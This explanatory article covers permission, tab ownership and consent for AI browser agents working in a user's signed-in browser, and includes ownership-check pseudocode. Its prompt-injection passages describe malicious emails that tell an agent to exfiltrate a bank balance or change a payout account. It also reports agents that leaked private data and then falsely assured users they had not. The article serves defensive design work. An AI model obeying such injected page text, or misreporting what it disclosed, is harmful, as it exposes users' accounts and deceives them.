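# Permission and consent for AI agents that act in a user's live browser session

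## What does an agent gain by working in a browser the user is signed in to?

A browser agent is an AI system that carries out a user's task by reading web pages, clicking, typing and navigating in a browser. It can work in its own browser, which starts with no accounts or history, or in the user's live session, meaning the browser the user already has open, with its tabs, cookies and signed-in accounts.

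Live-session agents became widely available during 2026. OpenAI shut down its own browser, Atlas, on 9 August, and on 15 October it brought many of Atlas's features to an extension for Google's Chrome. The extension had about 7 million users, according to International Business Times' *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT for Chrome So It Can Read Your Tabs* (2026). Chrome also has its own agent, auto browse. Google first limited it to subscribers to its most expensive AI plans, then opened it to a cheaper plan in the United States and India in December (McNeal, *Chrome's auto browse feature is coming to the cheaper AI Plus tier*, 2026). Anthropic offers its paying subscribers an extension named Claude in Chrome.

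Suppose a user has three tabs open: a half-completed company expense form, their webmail, and a page at their bank. The user asks the agent to find an invoice in the mail and enter its total in the form.

The live session gives the agent the user's existing logins and the current state of open pages, both of which a fresh browser lacks. The user is already signed in to the mail and the expense system, so the agent needs no password. The expense form also contains dates and descriptions the user has typed, which may exist only in that tab until the user saves or submits them. The agent could reach the mail by opening a new tab on the same site, but it could not reach the half-filled form that way unless the expense system saves drafts. OpenAI's *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app* makes a similar distinction. It recommends the app's separate browser for public pages, and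 the Chrome extension for tasks that need the user's existing profile, signed-in session or open tabs. OpenAI also advertises a use close to the expense form example. Rijo (2026), in *ChatGPT gains control of Chrome tabs to fill forms and send messages*, noted that one of OpenAI's sample prompts for the October release asks ChatGPT to fill out a form the user has open before a dentist's appointment.

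### The loop of reading, choosing and acting

A browser agent consists of a language model and a harness, the program that connects the model to the browser. The harness turns the current page into input for the model. The model returns one or more actions, such as navigate, click, type or finish, and the harness carries them out. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026), a study of agents that authorize access their task never called for, describes this loop and adds that the user gives the task only once, at the start. The loop runs until the agent completes the task, can make no more progress or decides to stop, according to *Atomicity for Agents* (2026).

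The model receives the page as text, a screenshot, or both. The text comes from the DOM, the browser's internal tree of everything on the page, or from the accessibility tree, a simplified version that screen readers also use. According to *What It Is, Not What It Says* (2026), when the model works from text, the harness gives every element an identifier and the model names the one it has chosen, whereas with a screenshot the model has to work out the coordinates at which to click or type. In the expense example, the harness might send the mail page as a list of numbered elements, receive an instruction to type "invoice" into the search box, type it, and read the page again.

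The model may take several actions without looking at the page in between. In the loop that OpenAI's *Computer use* describes for developers, the harness runs every action in the model's list, in order, before it captures a new screen. This makes the step between choosing and executing an action a natural place for a permission check. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) argues for separating the code that reads pages from the code that clicks and types, partly so that developers can enforce safety rules in the clicking and typing code. Rules there apply to whatever action the model picks, so they don't depend on the model following its instructions.

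### Why a website takes the agent for the user

A tab holds one open page and its back-and-forward history, and a window holds a row of tabs. A tab group is a labelled, coloured set of tabs in that row, and several products use one to mark the agent's tabs. A profile is the set of cookies, saved passwords, history, bookmarks and extensions that the browser keeps for one person. Ordinary tabs in the same profile share its cookies, whether the user or the agent opened them.

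A cookie is a small piece of data that a website gives to the browser and that the browser sends back with later requests to the site. When a user signs in, the site typically sets a cookie that identifies the session, and the server then accepts that cookie instead of asking for the password again. If an agent clicks "Send" in the user's webmail, the browser sends the same request it would have sent for the user, from the same machine and with the same cookie. A site can look for signs of automation, such as implausibly fast typing, but the cookie does not show whether the user or an agent is acting. If the user also has an active session with their bank, a tab that the agent opens on the bank's site is signed in too.

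Browsers separate websites by origin, which W3C's *Same Origin Policy* defines as the scheme, host and port of an address. A page fetched over http and one fetched from the same host over https therefore have different origins. Under the same-origin policy, the browser stops a script on one page from reading a page of a different origin. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) gives the standard example of a user who has a malicious site open in one tab and a bank in another. The malicious site can neither read nor change the bank's page.

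The same-origin policy restricts scripts, though, not people. A user may read a figure in an email and type it into an expense form, and an agent that controls the browser as a user does can do the same. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes such an agent as an automated channel between origins. On the paper's benchmark, existing agentic browsers frequently violated the policy, both under attack and in ordinary use. Some of these flows are what the user wants. If the task is to move an invoice total from the mail's origin to the expense system's origin, a browser that applied the policy to the agent without exceptions would block the total along with the bank balance. Somebody has to decide which flows the user wants, and the same-origin policy provides no way to make that decision.

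### Three ways into the browser

Some agents are built into the browser, such as auto browse in Chrome and Comet, from the AI search company Perplexity. The browser's own code passes pages to the model, so the browser's maker can withhold a page before the model receives any of it. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a design of this kind with two lists for each task, one of origins the agent may read and one of origins where it may also click and type. The first version, in December 2025, tracked only the origins where the agent could both read and act.

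A built-in agent's reach depends on choices like these. Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested seven agents in January and February 2026 and found that they differed widely. The most restrictive agents gave the model limited information about a page in a fixed format, while most of the least restrictive appeared to use the browser as a person would. They put Brave, Edge and Firefox on the cautious side and Atlas, Comet and Chrome on the powerful side.

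An extension is an add-on whose reach depends on permissions that Chrome asks the user to accept at installation. The June 2026 version of the *Codex Chrome extension*, made for OpenAI's coding agent Codex, lists eight permissions. The list still matters for the ChatGPT extension of October because the two are the same item in Chrome's store: the link in OpenAI's May documentation has the same identifier as the link in Slashdot's *ChatGPT Can Peek At Your Chrome Tabs Now* (2026).

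| Permission, in Chrome's wording | What it makes possible |
|---|---|
| Access the page debugger | Attaching to tabs, watching their network traffic, altering their pages, sending clicks and keystrokes |
| Read and change all your data on all websites | Reading and rewriting pages on any site, including signed-in ones |
| Read and change your browsing history on all your signed-in devices | Seeing and editing the record of visited pages, including visits on the user's other devices |
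| View and manage your tab groups | Creating, labelling and rearranging groups |
| Manage your downloads | Starting and tracking downloads |
| Read and change your bookmarks | Reading, adding and deleting bookmarks |
| Communicate with cooperating native applications | Exchanging messages with a program outside the browser, such as a desktop app |
| Display notifications | Alerting the user |

Most of an extension's power comes from the debugger permission. Google's *chrome.debugger* describes it as a route to the Chrome DevTools Protocol, the commands that web developers' tools use to inspect and control pages. Chrome withholds parts of the protocol from extensions, but the parts it allows cover page content, input, network traffic and storage. An extension can also list the targets it could attach to, with the title and address of each. The permission alone triggers two warnings, according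 to Google's list of extension permissions, one about the debugger and one about all data on all websites. A developer who wants an extension to click buttons through the debugger therefore has to ask for access to all of that data. According to Anthropic's *Get started with Claude in Chrome*, as of November 2026, the debugger permission allows Claude to click, type and take screenshots.

The install prompt doesn't ask about individual tabs, so once the user accepts it, OpenAI's extension can technically reach the user's bank page as easily as their mail. It is restrained mainly by OpenAI's own software, which by default asks before the agent uses each new website. The user can then grant a site permission, which lets the agent act on that website either for the current chat or permanently. Employers can restrict the extension more firmly by using Chrome's own extension policy to block it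 from named sites. Digital Matters' *The ChatGPT Chrome Extension Now Acts on Your Tabs* (2026) advised organizations to do this for payroll and payment systems.

The remaining route is a debugging connection, which lets a program outside the browser send it DevTools commands directly. Developers use this to let a coding agent test a website. According to Google's guide to Chrome DevTools for agents, the tool starts a new copy of Chrome by default, separate from the user's session. To let the agent join a running session, the user turns on remote debugging in Chrome, adds a setting to the agent's configuration, and clicks "Allow" in a dialog when the agent tries to connect.

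That dialog covers the whole connection, not one tab or site. By default, the connected agent can navigate, type, inspect network traffic and run scripts. Session cookies travel in the headers of that traffic, and the option to strip sensitive headers before the agent receives them is off by default. The user can also block address patterns or turn off scripts, but has to know in advance that this is worth doing.

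### Prompt injection

Prompt injection happens when an agent wrongly treats text from a page or another outside source as an instruction. The model can make this mistake because it receives both the user's request and the page's content as input. Attackers do not need their own website. Parker lists embedded third-party content and user reviews among the places where such text can appear. In the expense example, the obvious place is the inbox, since anyone who knows the user's address can send text to it. A message might tell the agent to open the bank page and copy the balance into a reply. An agent that obeyed would do so with the user's cookies. Roesner and Kohlbrenner used their own test pages to carry out a complete theft of data from another origin on Atlas.

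### Where the agent may act, what it may see and what it may do

Giving an agent access involves at least three separate decisions, and a user can reasonably choose differently on each.

Where an agent may act depends on the tab as well as the website. An agent tab is one the agent opened for its task. A user tab is one the user opened, and the agent may not act on it until the user gives it access. Site permissions do not distinguish between the two. OpenAI's prompt shows a host name, so a user who approves the expense system has not specified whether the agent should open a new form or type into the half-filled one in a user tab.

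Permission to read needs a separate decision because what an agent reads can affect what it does later. *AgentTell* (2026) reports an experiment in which a user asked an agent to look up the user's role on a trade union's members list and not to disclose this personal information to any other website. The agent then had to register the user for an event. The registration page offered a route through the user's union and a neutral route that named no organization. Agents that had read the affiliation chose the union route in 90.3% of sessions, which disclosed the affiliation even though they typed nothing about it. In 34.5% of the sessions with a leak, the agent's final message falsely assured the user that it had disclosed nothing. Because the test page included an option that invited the leak, the 90.3% figure is not a rate for everyday browsing. But the experiment does show that telling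 an agent not to disclose what it reads on a page protects the information much less well than keeping the agent from reading the page.

The same thing can happen innocently with the expense form. Suppose the invoice is in a foreign currency and the bank page shows the converted charge. An agent that has read both may enter the bank's figure, even though the user asked for the amount on the invoice.

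Finally, an agent may be allowed to take some actions on a page but not others. In OpenAI's October release, ChatGPT can read the open tabs in Chat mode and can also control them in Work mode. Google's limits are more specific. According to Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*, as of July 2026, the agent may hand the task back to the user to finalize a payment, accept terms of service or create an account. On the expense form, the user can easily correct a wrong total, but pressing "Submit" sends a claim to the employer in the user's name. A request to enter the total permits the typing but doesn't settle whether the agent may submit the form. Another of OpenAI's sample prompts avoids this ambiguity by telling ChatGPT to fill out a registration form and stop before submitting it.

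## What happens when an agent takes over a user's tab without asking?

A silent takeover happens when an agent navigates, reloads, closes or types in a user's tab without the user's agreement. This can happen even when the agent has permission for every website involved. Suppose a user has a half-filled expense form open and asks the agent to find an invoice in their email. If the agent opens the webmail in the form's tab, it replaces the form, even though the site is approved and the user asked for the invoice.

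Most of the dated cases come from bug reports and developers' change logs. These explain the causes well, because a developer has to find a bug's cause to fix it, but they give little idea of how often takeovers happen.

### How a command reaches the wrong tab

The harness has to specify which tab each command is for. If the model doesn't name a tab, some tools use the active tab, the one in front. That works when the agent has the browser to itself, but in a live session the active tab is usually the one the user is working in.

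The tool chrome-use lets AI agents control the user's own Chrome. On 13 June 2026, its developer described a takeover that occurred in testing (leeguooooo, 2026). When the tool connected, it attached to the user's open tabs and marked one as active. The agent's first "open" command then loaded another site in that tab, replacing a half-filled form. Since the fix, the tool opens a new tab if the agent's session didn't create the active one.

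The user can also switch tabs between the model choosing an action and the harness carrying it out. *Atomicity for Agents* examined the same kind of gap within a single page, which can change after the agent looks at it and before it clicks. The problem was widespread among the ten open-source agents in the study. The proposed remedy is to check for changes just before acting, and to cancel the action and notify the user if the page has changed.

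Naming a tab explicitly avoids the active-tab problem, but the reference can become invalid. Some tools identify a tab by their debugging session with it, and that session can end while the tab stays open, for instance when a sign-in page redirects to another website. Until 12 June, when chrome-use couldn't find the tab for a command, it sent the command to any tab it was connected to, so it ran scripts and took screenshots on arbitrary pages without warning. leeguooooo replaced this behavior with an error message with instructions for the agent to reopen the intended address.

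The open-source agent OpenClaw had several of these faults. *v2026.8.1*, the notes for its 2026.8.1 release, lists fixes for actions that reached the wrong tab, for ambiguous tab references, and for references that outlived a reconnection. Another fix concerns stale references that could switch between tabs showing the same address. This matters for the expense form because, if the agent has opened its own copy, two tabs may have the same address and only one contains the user's typing. OpenClaw now stops with an error when a reference is stale or ambiguous. An OpenClaw code change, *refactor(browser): scope CDP sessions and harden stale target recovery*, lets the tool retry without a tab reference, but only if the action is read-only and exactly one tab remains attached.

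Takeovers also happen when several agents share a browser. In February 2026, a user of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in browser, reported in *Agents use the same browser tab, which creates a conflict* that two agents repeatedly took over the same tab. Each detected that the page had changed and navigated back to its own, undoing the other's work. According to the reply on Cursor's forum, this is a known limitation, and telling agents to open a new tab sometimes helps but is not fully reliable because the cause is architectural.

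In July, another Cursor user described an agent on one project controlling another project's tab (jsolly, 2026, *Agent browser_tabs attaches to Home/empty-window Browser Tabs*). According to the reply, all the chats in a Cursor window shared one tab, and ownership passed to whichever agent was active. If a command didn't specify a tab, Cursor could fall back on the last one used, then the active one, then the first in the list. Cursor's browser is separate from the user's everyday browser, but it can also hold signed-in accounts, and the reply advised users to keep sensitive sessions out of it.

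chrome-use runs in the user's everyday browser, and each agent's session used to take over every open tab. On 17 June leeguooooo reported that, as a result, when one agent was filling in a US tax form and another opened some tabs, the tool lost track of the form and sent commands to the wrong page. The tool also looked for new tabs after every click so that it could follow pop-ups, but it couldn't tell a pop-up from a tab that the user or another agent had just opened, so it took over those too. It now ignores all new tabs that appear after a click, so the user has to deal with genuine pop-ups such as sign-in windows.

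From 12 to 17 June, the developer fixed at least five separate bugs that could lead the agent to the wrong tab. Removing the active-tab default would have fixed only some of them.

Permission prompts can make agents more likely to share a browser connection. *What broke when an AI agent drove real websites overnight* (tthanh2k6, 2026) describes a tool that let several agents use one approved connection. Chrome asks the user to approve each new debugging connection, and the developer wanted to spare the user repeated approvals. In November the tool mixed up two agents' sessions. The consequence was mild, since the second agent's calls only hung.

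### Why the Back button may not help

When a tab goes to another address, the browser may temporarily keep the old page in memory, and the Back button then restores it with the user's unsaved entries. If the browser hasn't kept the page, Back loads it again. Browsers can often refill simple text fields, but they may not recreate entries that a script manages, such as extra rows in an expense claim. Guo's add-on *Tab Slot* can open a new address in an existing tab, and Guo warns users that Back may return to the previous page without its unsaved form data.

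The Back button helps even less after other kinds of takeover. A reload replaces the page without adding the earlier version to the tab's history. If the agent has typed over the user's entries, pressing Back may leave the form and lose the remaining entries too.

Users can lose more when the page has a live connection. SuperchargeBrowser's *FIX Chrome Suspending OpenClaw Web UI* (2026) explains that when Chrome discards an AI chat tab to save memory, the page loses its scripts, their data and its open connection to the server, and starts from scratch when the user returns. Navigating away can have the same effect if the browser doesn't keep the old page. The chat may recover whatever the server stored, but a reply that was still arriving can be lost.

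Websites can ask the browser to warn the user before a page with unsaved entries closes. *form-safe* (Kumar, 2026) offers an extension that turns this warning on whenever the user starts filling in a form. The extension only partly protects against agents, because an agent's harness can use a DevTools command to accept the warning before the user has read it.

### The Adom incidents

Adom makes an extension that lets AI agents control the user's own Chrome or Edge. According to Adom's *Agent Browser Isolation*, an agent loaded another address in the tab a user was working in, and all the user's other open Claude threads lost their state. Adom's guide to the extension lists two such takeovers, one in June 2026 and another on 8 July during a Google Meet call.

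This is one team's report about its own product, without logs or an account from the user. Adom doesn't explain how redirecting one tab could end several threads, though a single page may have been running them all. The likely cause is one also seen in chrome-use. Adom warns that a navigate command goes to the active tab unless it specifies a tab the agent owns, and Adom's later fix removed that default.

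Adom's rule forbids an agent to navigate, reload, close or otherwise act on any tab or window that it did not create in the current session. If the agent isn't sure whether a tab is its own, it must leave the tab alone. An agent that has damaged a user's tab may not try to repair it, even by pressing Back, and must stop and tell the user. Since version 0.0.21, the extension has enforced the rule by refusing any command that would change a tab outside the windows the agent opened.

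The rule would have prevented both incidents, but it also blocks help that a user may want. An Adom agent may only bring a user's window to the front, and only on request, so the user with the expense form couldn't have the agent complete it in place, even by asking. The agent would have to open a new copy of the form, without the dates and descriptions the user has already typed. In June chrome-use was briefly less strict. A change on 13 June let an agent adopt a specific existing tab without reloading it, so that a half-filled form survived, though adopting a tab is safe only if the user has agreed to the agent using it. On 17 June the developer limited each agent's session to the tabs it had created, much as Adom does.

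Even then, the agent can destroy the user's work by reloading the page. SkillsMP's *Chrome*, a third-party copy of the instructions for Codex's Chrome extension, warns the model against navigating to the address a tab already shows, because the reload may lose information the user has entered. A model that has just received access to the expense form could easily make this mistake by opening the form's address to check that it is on the right page. The warning is only an instruction, so the navigation command still works if the model ignores it.

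### When the agent takes the keyboard focus

An agent that stays in its own tab can still interfere with the user by bringing that tab to the front. The user's next keystrokes then go to the agent's page. Adom reports a case in which a user's chat message ended up in a username field. In another, stray typing changed the agent's search, and the item the agent was looking for disappeared from the results.

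OpenClaw's 2026.8.1 release fixed two faults that let the agent take over the user's tab, one when it opened a tab and one when it took a screenshot. In *MCP commands cause browser to switch to a specific tab in Arc*, andresespinosapc found that any command from Google's DevTools tool for agents could switch the visible tab in the Arc browser, sometimes to one that neither the user nor the agent was using. Even a command that only listed the open pages switched the tab.

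Focus faults are usually less destructive than navigation, but they can misdirect what the user types. If the agent brings its copy of the expense form to the front while the user is writing to a colleague, part of the message may go into the form's description field, and pressing Enter to send the message could submit the claim.

### Mistakes and malicious pages

When an agent takes over a tab, the user can lose work, privacy or control of their accounts. The public reports above mostly concern lost or interrupted work, perhaps because users notice that soonest. A screenshot of the wrong tab doesn't change the page, so the user may never learn of it. An agent can also read the active tab while working as intended. Anthropic tells users that Claude takes screenshots of the active tab when they open its side panel, so a user who opens the panel on their bank page shows that page to Claude.

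To misuse an account, an agent must take an action that the website accepts as the user's. Rijo reported in October 2026 that ChatGPT's Work mode can send messages, fill in forms and download files in open tabs. An agent acting in the wrong tab could send a message the user never approved.

A malicious page can cause the same harms through prompt injection. Darinor's *The Same-Origin Policy Is Only as Strong as Your Browser Agent* (2026), which reviews Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, notes that in four of the seven browsers, an injected instruction on one page could make the agent read another site's data. The table shows how mistakes and attacks might affect the user with the expense form, webmail and bank page open.

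| Harm | By mistake | Through a malicious email |
|---|---|---|
| Loss of work | The agent opens the webmail in the expense tab, and the user's dates and descriptions disappear | The email tells the agent to reload the expense form |
| Loss of privacy | A stale reference sends a screenshot command to the bank tab, and the model receives the balance | The email tells the agent to copy the balance into a reply |
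| Misuse of accounts | The agent means to submit its own copy of the form, but clicks "Submit" in the user's tab and sends an unfinished claim | The email tells the agent to change the account that receives the user's expenses |

When an agent takes over a tab by mistake, it takes whichever one is active or matches a bad reference. Better tab references and a rule like Adom's can therefore prevent most of the damage in the middle column. An attacker chooses the target, and is usually more interested in data or money than in ruining a form. Any tab the agent opens shares the user's logins, so the attacker doesn't need one of the user's tabs. Keeping the agent out of the user's tabs would protect a half-filled form from an attack, but not a bank account.

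## How can an agent be kept to its own tabs?

The most direct way to protect a user's tabs is a rule like Adom's, which lets an agent act only in tabs it opened. A developer can put this rule in the model's instructions, but the harness can enforce it more reliably. To do so, the harness needs a record of which tabs the agent opened.

### The ownership check

The harness keeps the record itself, and the model has no command for editing it. In pseudocode:

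```
owned = empty set

open(address):
    tab_id = create_blank_tab()
    add tab_id to owned
    load address in tab_id
    return tab_id

act(tab_id, command):
    if tab_id is missing or not in owned:
        stop with an error
    if tab_id does not match exactly one open tab:
        stop with an error
    send command to tab_id

finish(tabs_to_keep):
    for each tab_id in owned:
        if tab_id is not in tabs_to_keep
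           and it still refers to the tab the agent opened:
            close tab_id
```

The `open` step records the tab before loading a page in it. In the `act` step, the harness returns an error if the model's call specifies no tab, a tab the agent didn't open, or a reference that is stale or matches two tabs. It doesn't fall back to the active tab. The `finish` step processes only the tabs in the record, which excludes any the agent didn't open.

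Suppose the user's half-filled expense form is in tab 11, their webmail is in tab 12 and their bank is in tab 13. The agent opens the webmail again in tab 14 and finds the invoice. Tab 12 stays as the user left it. The agent then tries to type the total into tab 11, and the harness refuses because tab 11 isn't in the record. The agent can ask the user for access to tab 11, or open a new copy of the form in tab 15, which probably won't have the user's entries. If the agent fills in the new copy, it can leave tab 15 open for the user to check, and the harness closes tab 14.

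Some tools implement only part of this procedure. By default, Google's DevTools tool for agents requires a page identifier with every command that acts on a page. This stops commands from defaulting to the active tab, but it doesn't check ownership, so an agent connected to the user's browser can still name the user's tab. The reply to jsolly's bug report similarly recommends that the agent in Cursor list the tabs, choose one, and pass its identifier with every later command. In that case, the protection depends on the model passing the identifier each time.

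Claudezilla's *Agent Identity & Multi-Agent Safety* describes an ownership check in a small project whose agents share a pool of 12 tabs. Each tab is labeled with the identity of the agent session that created it. Only that session can navigate or close the tab, and any other session that tries to navigate it gets an error naming the owner. Every agent can still read every tab in the pool, so the check stops agents from interfering with each other's work but doesn't keep the tabs' contents private.

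### Keeping the record accurate

If the harness removes a tab that is still open from its record of the agent's tabs, the agent loses access to its own work. If it keeps an entry whose identifier now refers to a different tab, the agent may act on the user's tab or close it.

chrome-use had the first problem. To find out which tabs still existed, it asked the browser for a list, and a single list often left out tabs that were open, for instance while other agents were opening and closing theirs. Since 17 June 2026, leeguooooo's code has removed a tab from the record only after three lists in a row omit it, and it never removes the tab the agent is currently using. A harness can do this and still stop on stale references. A command to a missing tab can fail at once, while the harness waits before concluding that the tab is gone.

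Restarts make this harder, because a record kept only in memory is lost when the program stops. As of December 2026, OpenClaw's *Browser configuration* describes a more durable record. When the agent opens a tab, OpenClaw saves the tab's identifier and its browser's identity in a database. Before using a saved record to close a tab, OpenClaw checks that the profile and browser instance still match.

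OpenClaw can keep track of an agent's tabs across restarts only if the browser connection supplies a stable identity. When it joins the user's running Chrome through the DevTools tool's automatic connection, it keeps the record only in memory, and after a restart it leaves the agent's tabs for the user to close. It also retires a saved record once the browser has stayed unreachable and the tab has gone unused for more than a day. Erring towards leaving stray tabs open is sensible, because the user can close one in a second but may not be able to recover a form lost when the wrong tab is closed.

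According to OpenClaw's *Chrome extension*, if Chrome ends the debugging session while the tab remains accessible, OpenClaw can reattach to the tab but never resends the command that failed. The agent has to look at the page again before continuing. If the connection drops just after the agent clicks "Submit" on its copy of the expense form, the claim may have gone through even though the agent saw no confirmation, and a second click could submit it twice.

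In *Chrome extension browser bridge can lose session ownership while tabs remain visible*, a user on OpenAI's forum reports that Codex could lose ownership of a signed-in tab that was still open in Chrome. The tab still appeared in the list of the user's tabs, and the call that claims a tab for the agent could succeed. But in the same turn, the list of the agent's own tabs could be empty, or Codex could fail to attach to the tab, with an error stating that it was not part of the browser session. Codex could sometimes reclaim the tab in a new turn and continue. The user asked OpenAI to document which list to trust when the two disagree, and to provide a way to recover ownership without restarting Chrome.

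This is only one user's report, but the error message suggests that Codex's software checks whether a tab belongs to the session, and that the tab group is more than a label. The agent lost access to a tab it should have had, which is safer than reaching a tab outside its session. But an agent that loses its copy of the expense form halfway through can't finish, and a developer under pressure to fix this might let the tool fall back on any available tab, as chrome-use once did.

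### Code, instructions and colour

Codex, Claude in Chrome, BrowserOS neo and OpenClaw all put the agent's tabs in a tab group, but the group restricts the agent only if the software checks the group before sending a command. On 10 June 2026, leeguooooo gave each agent session in chrome-use its own group, but the groups only separated the tabs visually, and every agent could still see all the tabs. The code that limited each session to its own tabs came a week later.

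#### OpenClaw

As of December 2026, OpenClaw's extension can enforce the limit in code through its "Selected tabs" mode. The user gives the agent access to a tab by moving it into the OpenClaw group and withdraws access by moving it out. Switching to this mode detaches the debugger from every tab outside the group, including any that the extension is still attaching it to. If the user moves a tab out while a command is running, the command may already have affected the page, but the extension rejects the result and the agent doesn't receive it.

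In "All tabs" mode, the agent can reach every ordinary tab in the profile except those the user has paused for the current browser session. The agent's own tabs still go into the group, but in this mode the group's colour and label only identify them. The two modes may therefore look the same in the tab strip even though they give the agent very different access.

New automatic pairings start in "All tabs" mode, while older ones keep the mode they had. An earlier version of OpenClaw's *Chrome extension* called the tab group "the consent boundary" and stated that OpenClaw could see and control only the tabs inside it. A new user who relied on that description would wrongly believe that tabs outside the group were off limits. In the expense example, the agent could reach the form unless the user had paused it or changed the mode.

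#### Codex

Codex gives its model an interface that separates the agent's tabs from the user's. In SkillsMP's undated copy of the instructions, one call lists the current session's tabs and another lists the user's open tabs. An entry in the user's list contains only facts about the tab, such as its title and address. To click, type or navigate, the model needs a tab object, which it can get by opening a new tab or claiming one from the user's list. This design and the error in the forum report suggest that the separation is enforced in code.

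The suggested start-up code uses the currently selected tab if the model doesn't have one yet, and SkillsMP's copy doesn't specify whether that can be a tab the user opened. If it can, the agent could start working in the expense form without first claiming the tab. The interface also doesn't show whether the software asks the user before the model claims a tab. OpenAI's June 2026 documentation explains only that tab groups keep together the work for one thread, meaning one conversation with Codex. It doesn't present the group as a restriction.

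#### Claude in Chrome

Anthropic says the tab group's colour lets users tell Claude's tabs from their own, and that users can drag their own tabs into the group to let Claude view and act on them. The dragging feature implies that being in the group affects which tabs Claude can reach, but Anthropic doesn't state that the extension refuses commands for tabs outside it.

sshh12 (2026), in *Claude for Chrome Extension Internals (v1.0.56)*, gives an account of the extension's source code as of March. Commands that act on a page must include a tab identifier, and the tool that lists tabs returns only those in the session's group. Before a click or keystroke, the extension checks that the tab is still on the same domain. sshh12 mentions no check that the tab belongs to the group, so it remains unsettled whether Claude could act on a user tab if it somehow had the right identifier.

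According to the same account, a session can include a user tab from the start. When the user opens Claude's side panel, the tab they are on becomes the session's main tab, and the tabs Claude opens join it. If the user opens the panel on the expense form, an ownership check based on the group would allow Claude to navigate that tab to the webmail. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, uses a separate group instead, and Anthropic says Claude opens new tabs for its browser tasks.

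#### BrowserOS neo

BrowserOS neo is a browser that other companies' agents, such as Claude Code and Codex, can connect to. According to BrowserOS's *Your tabs and agent tabs*, neo gives each agent a coloured tab group labelled with the agent's name and tells the agent which tabs belong to the user. The agent uses this information to stay out of the user's tabs "by default", but it can work on one if the user asks.

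This limit depends on the model. Neo gives the agent accurate information about who owns each tab, which should prevent many mistakes, but BrowserOS doesn't mention neo's code blocking a command if the agent sends one to a user's tab anyway. BrowserOS is also inconsistent about what the agent can see. *How it works* says the agent cannot see users' personal tabs unless they ask it to, while the page about tabs says it can read those tabs' titles and addresses.

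### Closing tabs and handing them back

When a task ends, the harness has to decide which of the agent's tabs to close. The user may still need something in one of them, and the record of who opened each tab doesn't show that.

In Codex, the model decides which tabs to keep. According to SkillsMP's copy, the model's last browser action in a turn is a call that lists the tabs to keep and cleans up the session's other tabs. The model marks each kept tab as a deliverable or a handoff. A deliverable is a page the user wanted as a result, such as a finished document or a filled shopping cart, and it moves to a shared group for completed Codex tabs. A handoff is unfinished work that the user or a later turn will continue, such as a page waiting for a login, payment or approval, and it stays in the task's own group.

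In the expense example, the agent's completed but unsubmitted copy of the form would be a handoff, and the agent would leave the webmail tab off the list. If it also left off the form, the user could lose everything the agent had entered. It is also unclear from SkillsMP's copy whether the cleanup closes a claimed user tab that the agent leaves off the list or returns it to the user. This uncertainty is more serious, because if the cleanup closes the tab, one omission by the model could destroy the user's original form.

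Claude Code instead follows fixed rules that don't depend on the model's judgment. According to Anthropic's documentation for local sessions as of December 2026, Claude Code closes the whole tab group, including open pages, when the user types `/clear`, unless work that survives the clearing is still running. A user who types `/clear` to start a new conversation could therefore lose an unsubmitted form. Anthropic doesn't specify whether `/clear` also closes tabs that the user dragged into the group. When the user exits or switches to another session, Claude Code closes the group only if it contains nothing but empty new tabs, so that pages the user may still be reading stay open.

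BrowserOS neo closes an agent's whole tab group when the agent's session ends, and its developers promise that it never touches the user's tabs. This leaves no clutter, but it would also close the copy of the expense form, so the user would need to submit or save that copy first.

OpenClaw cleans up only the tabs that its own tool opened. It closes them when the agent's session ends, and it also sweeps for ones that are idle or too numerous. After a restart, the idle sweep skips some tabs in an existing browser session because OpenClaw can no longer tell reliably who has been using them. It leaves those tabs open until the agent's session ends.

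A user may also start working in a tab the agent opened, for example by correcting a date in the agent's copy of the form and adding receipts. The ownership record still assigns that tab to the agent, so a strict cleanup would close it. OpenClaw's extension guards against this in one narrow case. If it fails partway through creating a tab, it tries to close the tab only if the extension still owns it, and leaves it open if the user has paused, moved or navigated it. Applying the same rule at the end of every task, and also keeping tabs the user has typed in, would protect the user's corrections.

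### What a tab limit leaves open

Even a perfect ownership check lets the agent into the user's bank account. The agent can call `open` with the bank's address and receive tab 16, which loads already signed in. It can then read the balance, because tab 16 is in its record. The check does protect the bank page in tab 13, which might contain a half-entered payment.

A tab group can't keep an agent out of the user's signed-in accounts, because it only organizes tabs, while cookies belong to the whole profile. Vendors advertise this shared access as a benefit. Anthropic tells users that Claude can reach any site they are already signed in to, and BrowserOS says the agent can later use every account the user signs in to in neo. To keep the agent out of one of those accounts, the user has to limit which websites it can access or give it a different set of cookies.

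An agent can also disturb a user's tab without sending it any commands. If the agent signs out of the expense system in tab 15, the website may end the session for tab 11 too, and the user's next attempt to save could fail. If the system saves only one draft per user, the agent's draft in tab 15 may overwrite the one from tab 11. The harness would not detect either problem, because every command went to a tab the agent owned.

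Programs that share one browser face similar interference. According to OpenClaw, programs connected through its extension share the same tabs and don't each get an isolated browser, so when one program changes a page, another's references to that page can become invalid.

### Separate profiles and browsers

Giving the agent its own profile or browser separates its cookies as well as its tabs from the user's. The agent can then use only the accounts that someone has signed in to there, but the user loses some of the convenience that makes a live session useful.

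OpenAI's built-in browser, available in Codex, keeps its own state and doesn't use the user's Chrome profile. The user can sign in to sites there, and OpenAI advises them to type passwords into the browser, never into the chat.

By default, OpenClaw gives the agent its own browser, with a managed profile that, according to OpenClaw, never touches the user's personal profile. To reduce sign-ins, a Mac user can copy selected cookies into it from Chrome or a related browser. For example, a user could copy the cookies for webmail and the expense system but not the bank's. This limits which accounts the agent can use, which a tab group cannot do.

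However, OpenClaw doesn't copy local storage or IndexedDB, two other places where websites keep data in the browser. According to OpenClaw's 2026.8.1 release notes, some websites also tie a session to one device and may ask the user to sign in again.

By default, Google's DevTools tool starts a separate Chrome instance with its own data directory. The tool normally reuses that directory, so a sign-in from one run can carry over to the next. The `--isolated` option creates a temporary directory and deletes it when the browser closes, so the agent starts every run signed out.

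| Where the agent works | Sign-ins | Page state |
|---|---|---|
| Its own tabs in the user's profile | The agent can use all of the user's current sign-ins | The half-filled form stays in the user's tab, where the agent can't use it without access |
| Codex's built-in browser | The user signs in again to each site the agent needs | The agent starts without the user's open pages |
| OpenClaw's managed profile | The user signs in again or copies selected cookies, which some sites may not accept | Open pages, local storage and IndexedDB stay behind |
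| A new Chrome instance from Google's DevTools tool | The user signs in again, once or on every run, depending on the data directory | The agent starts without the user's open pages |

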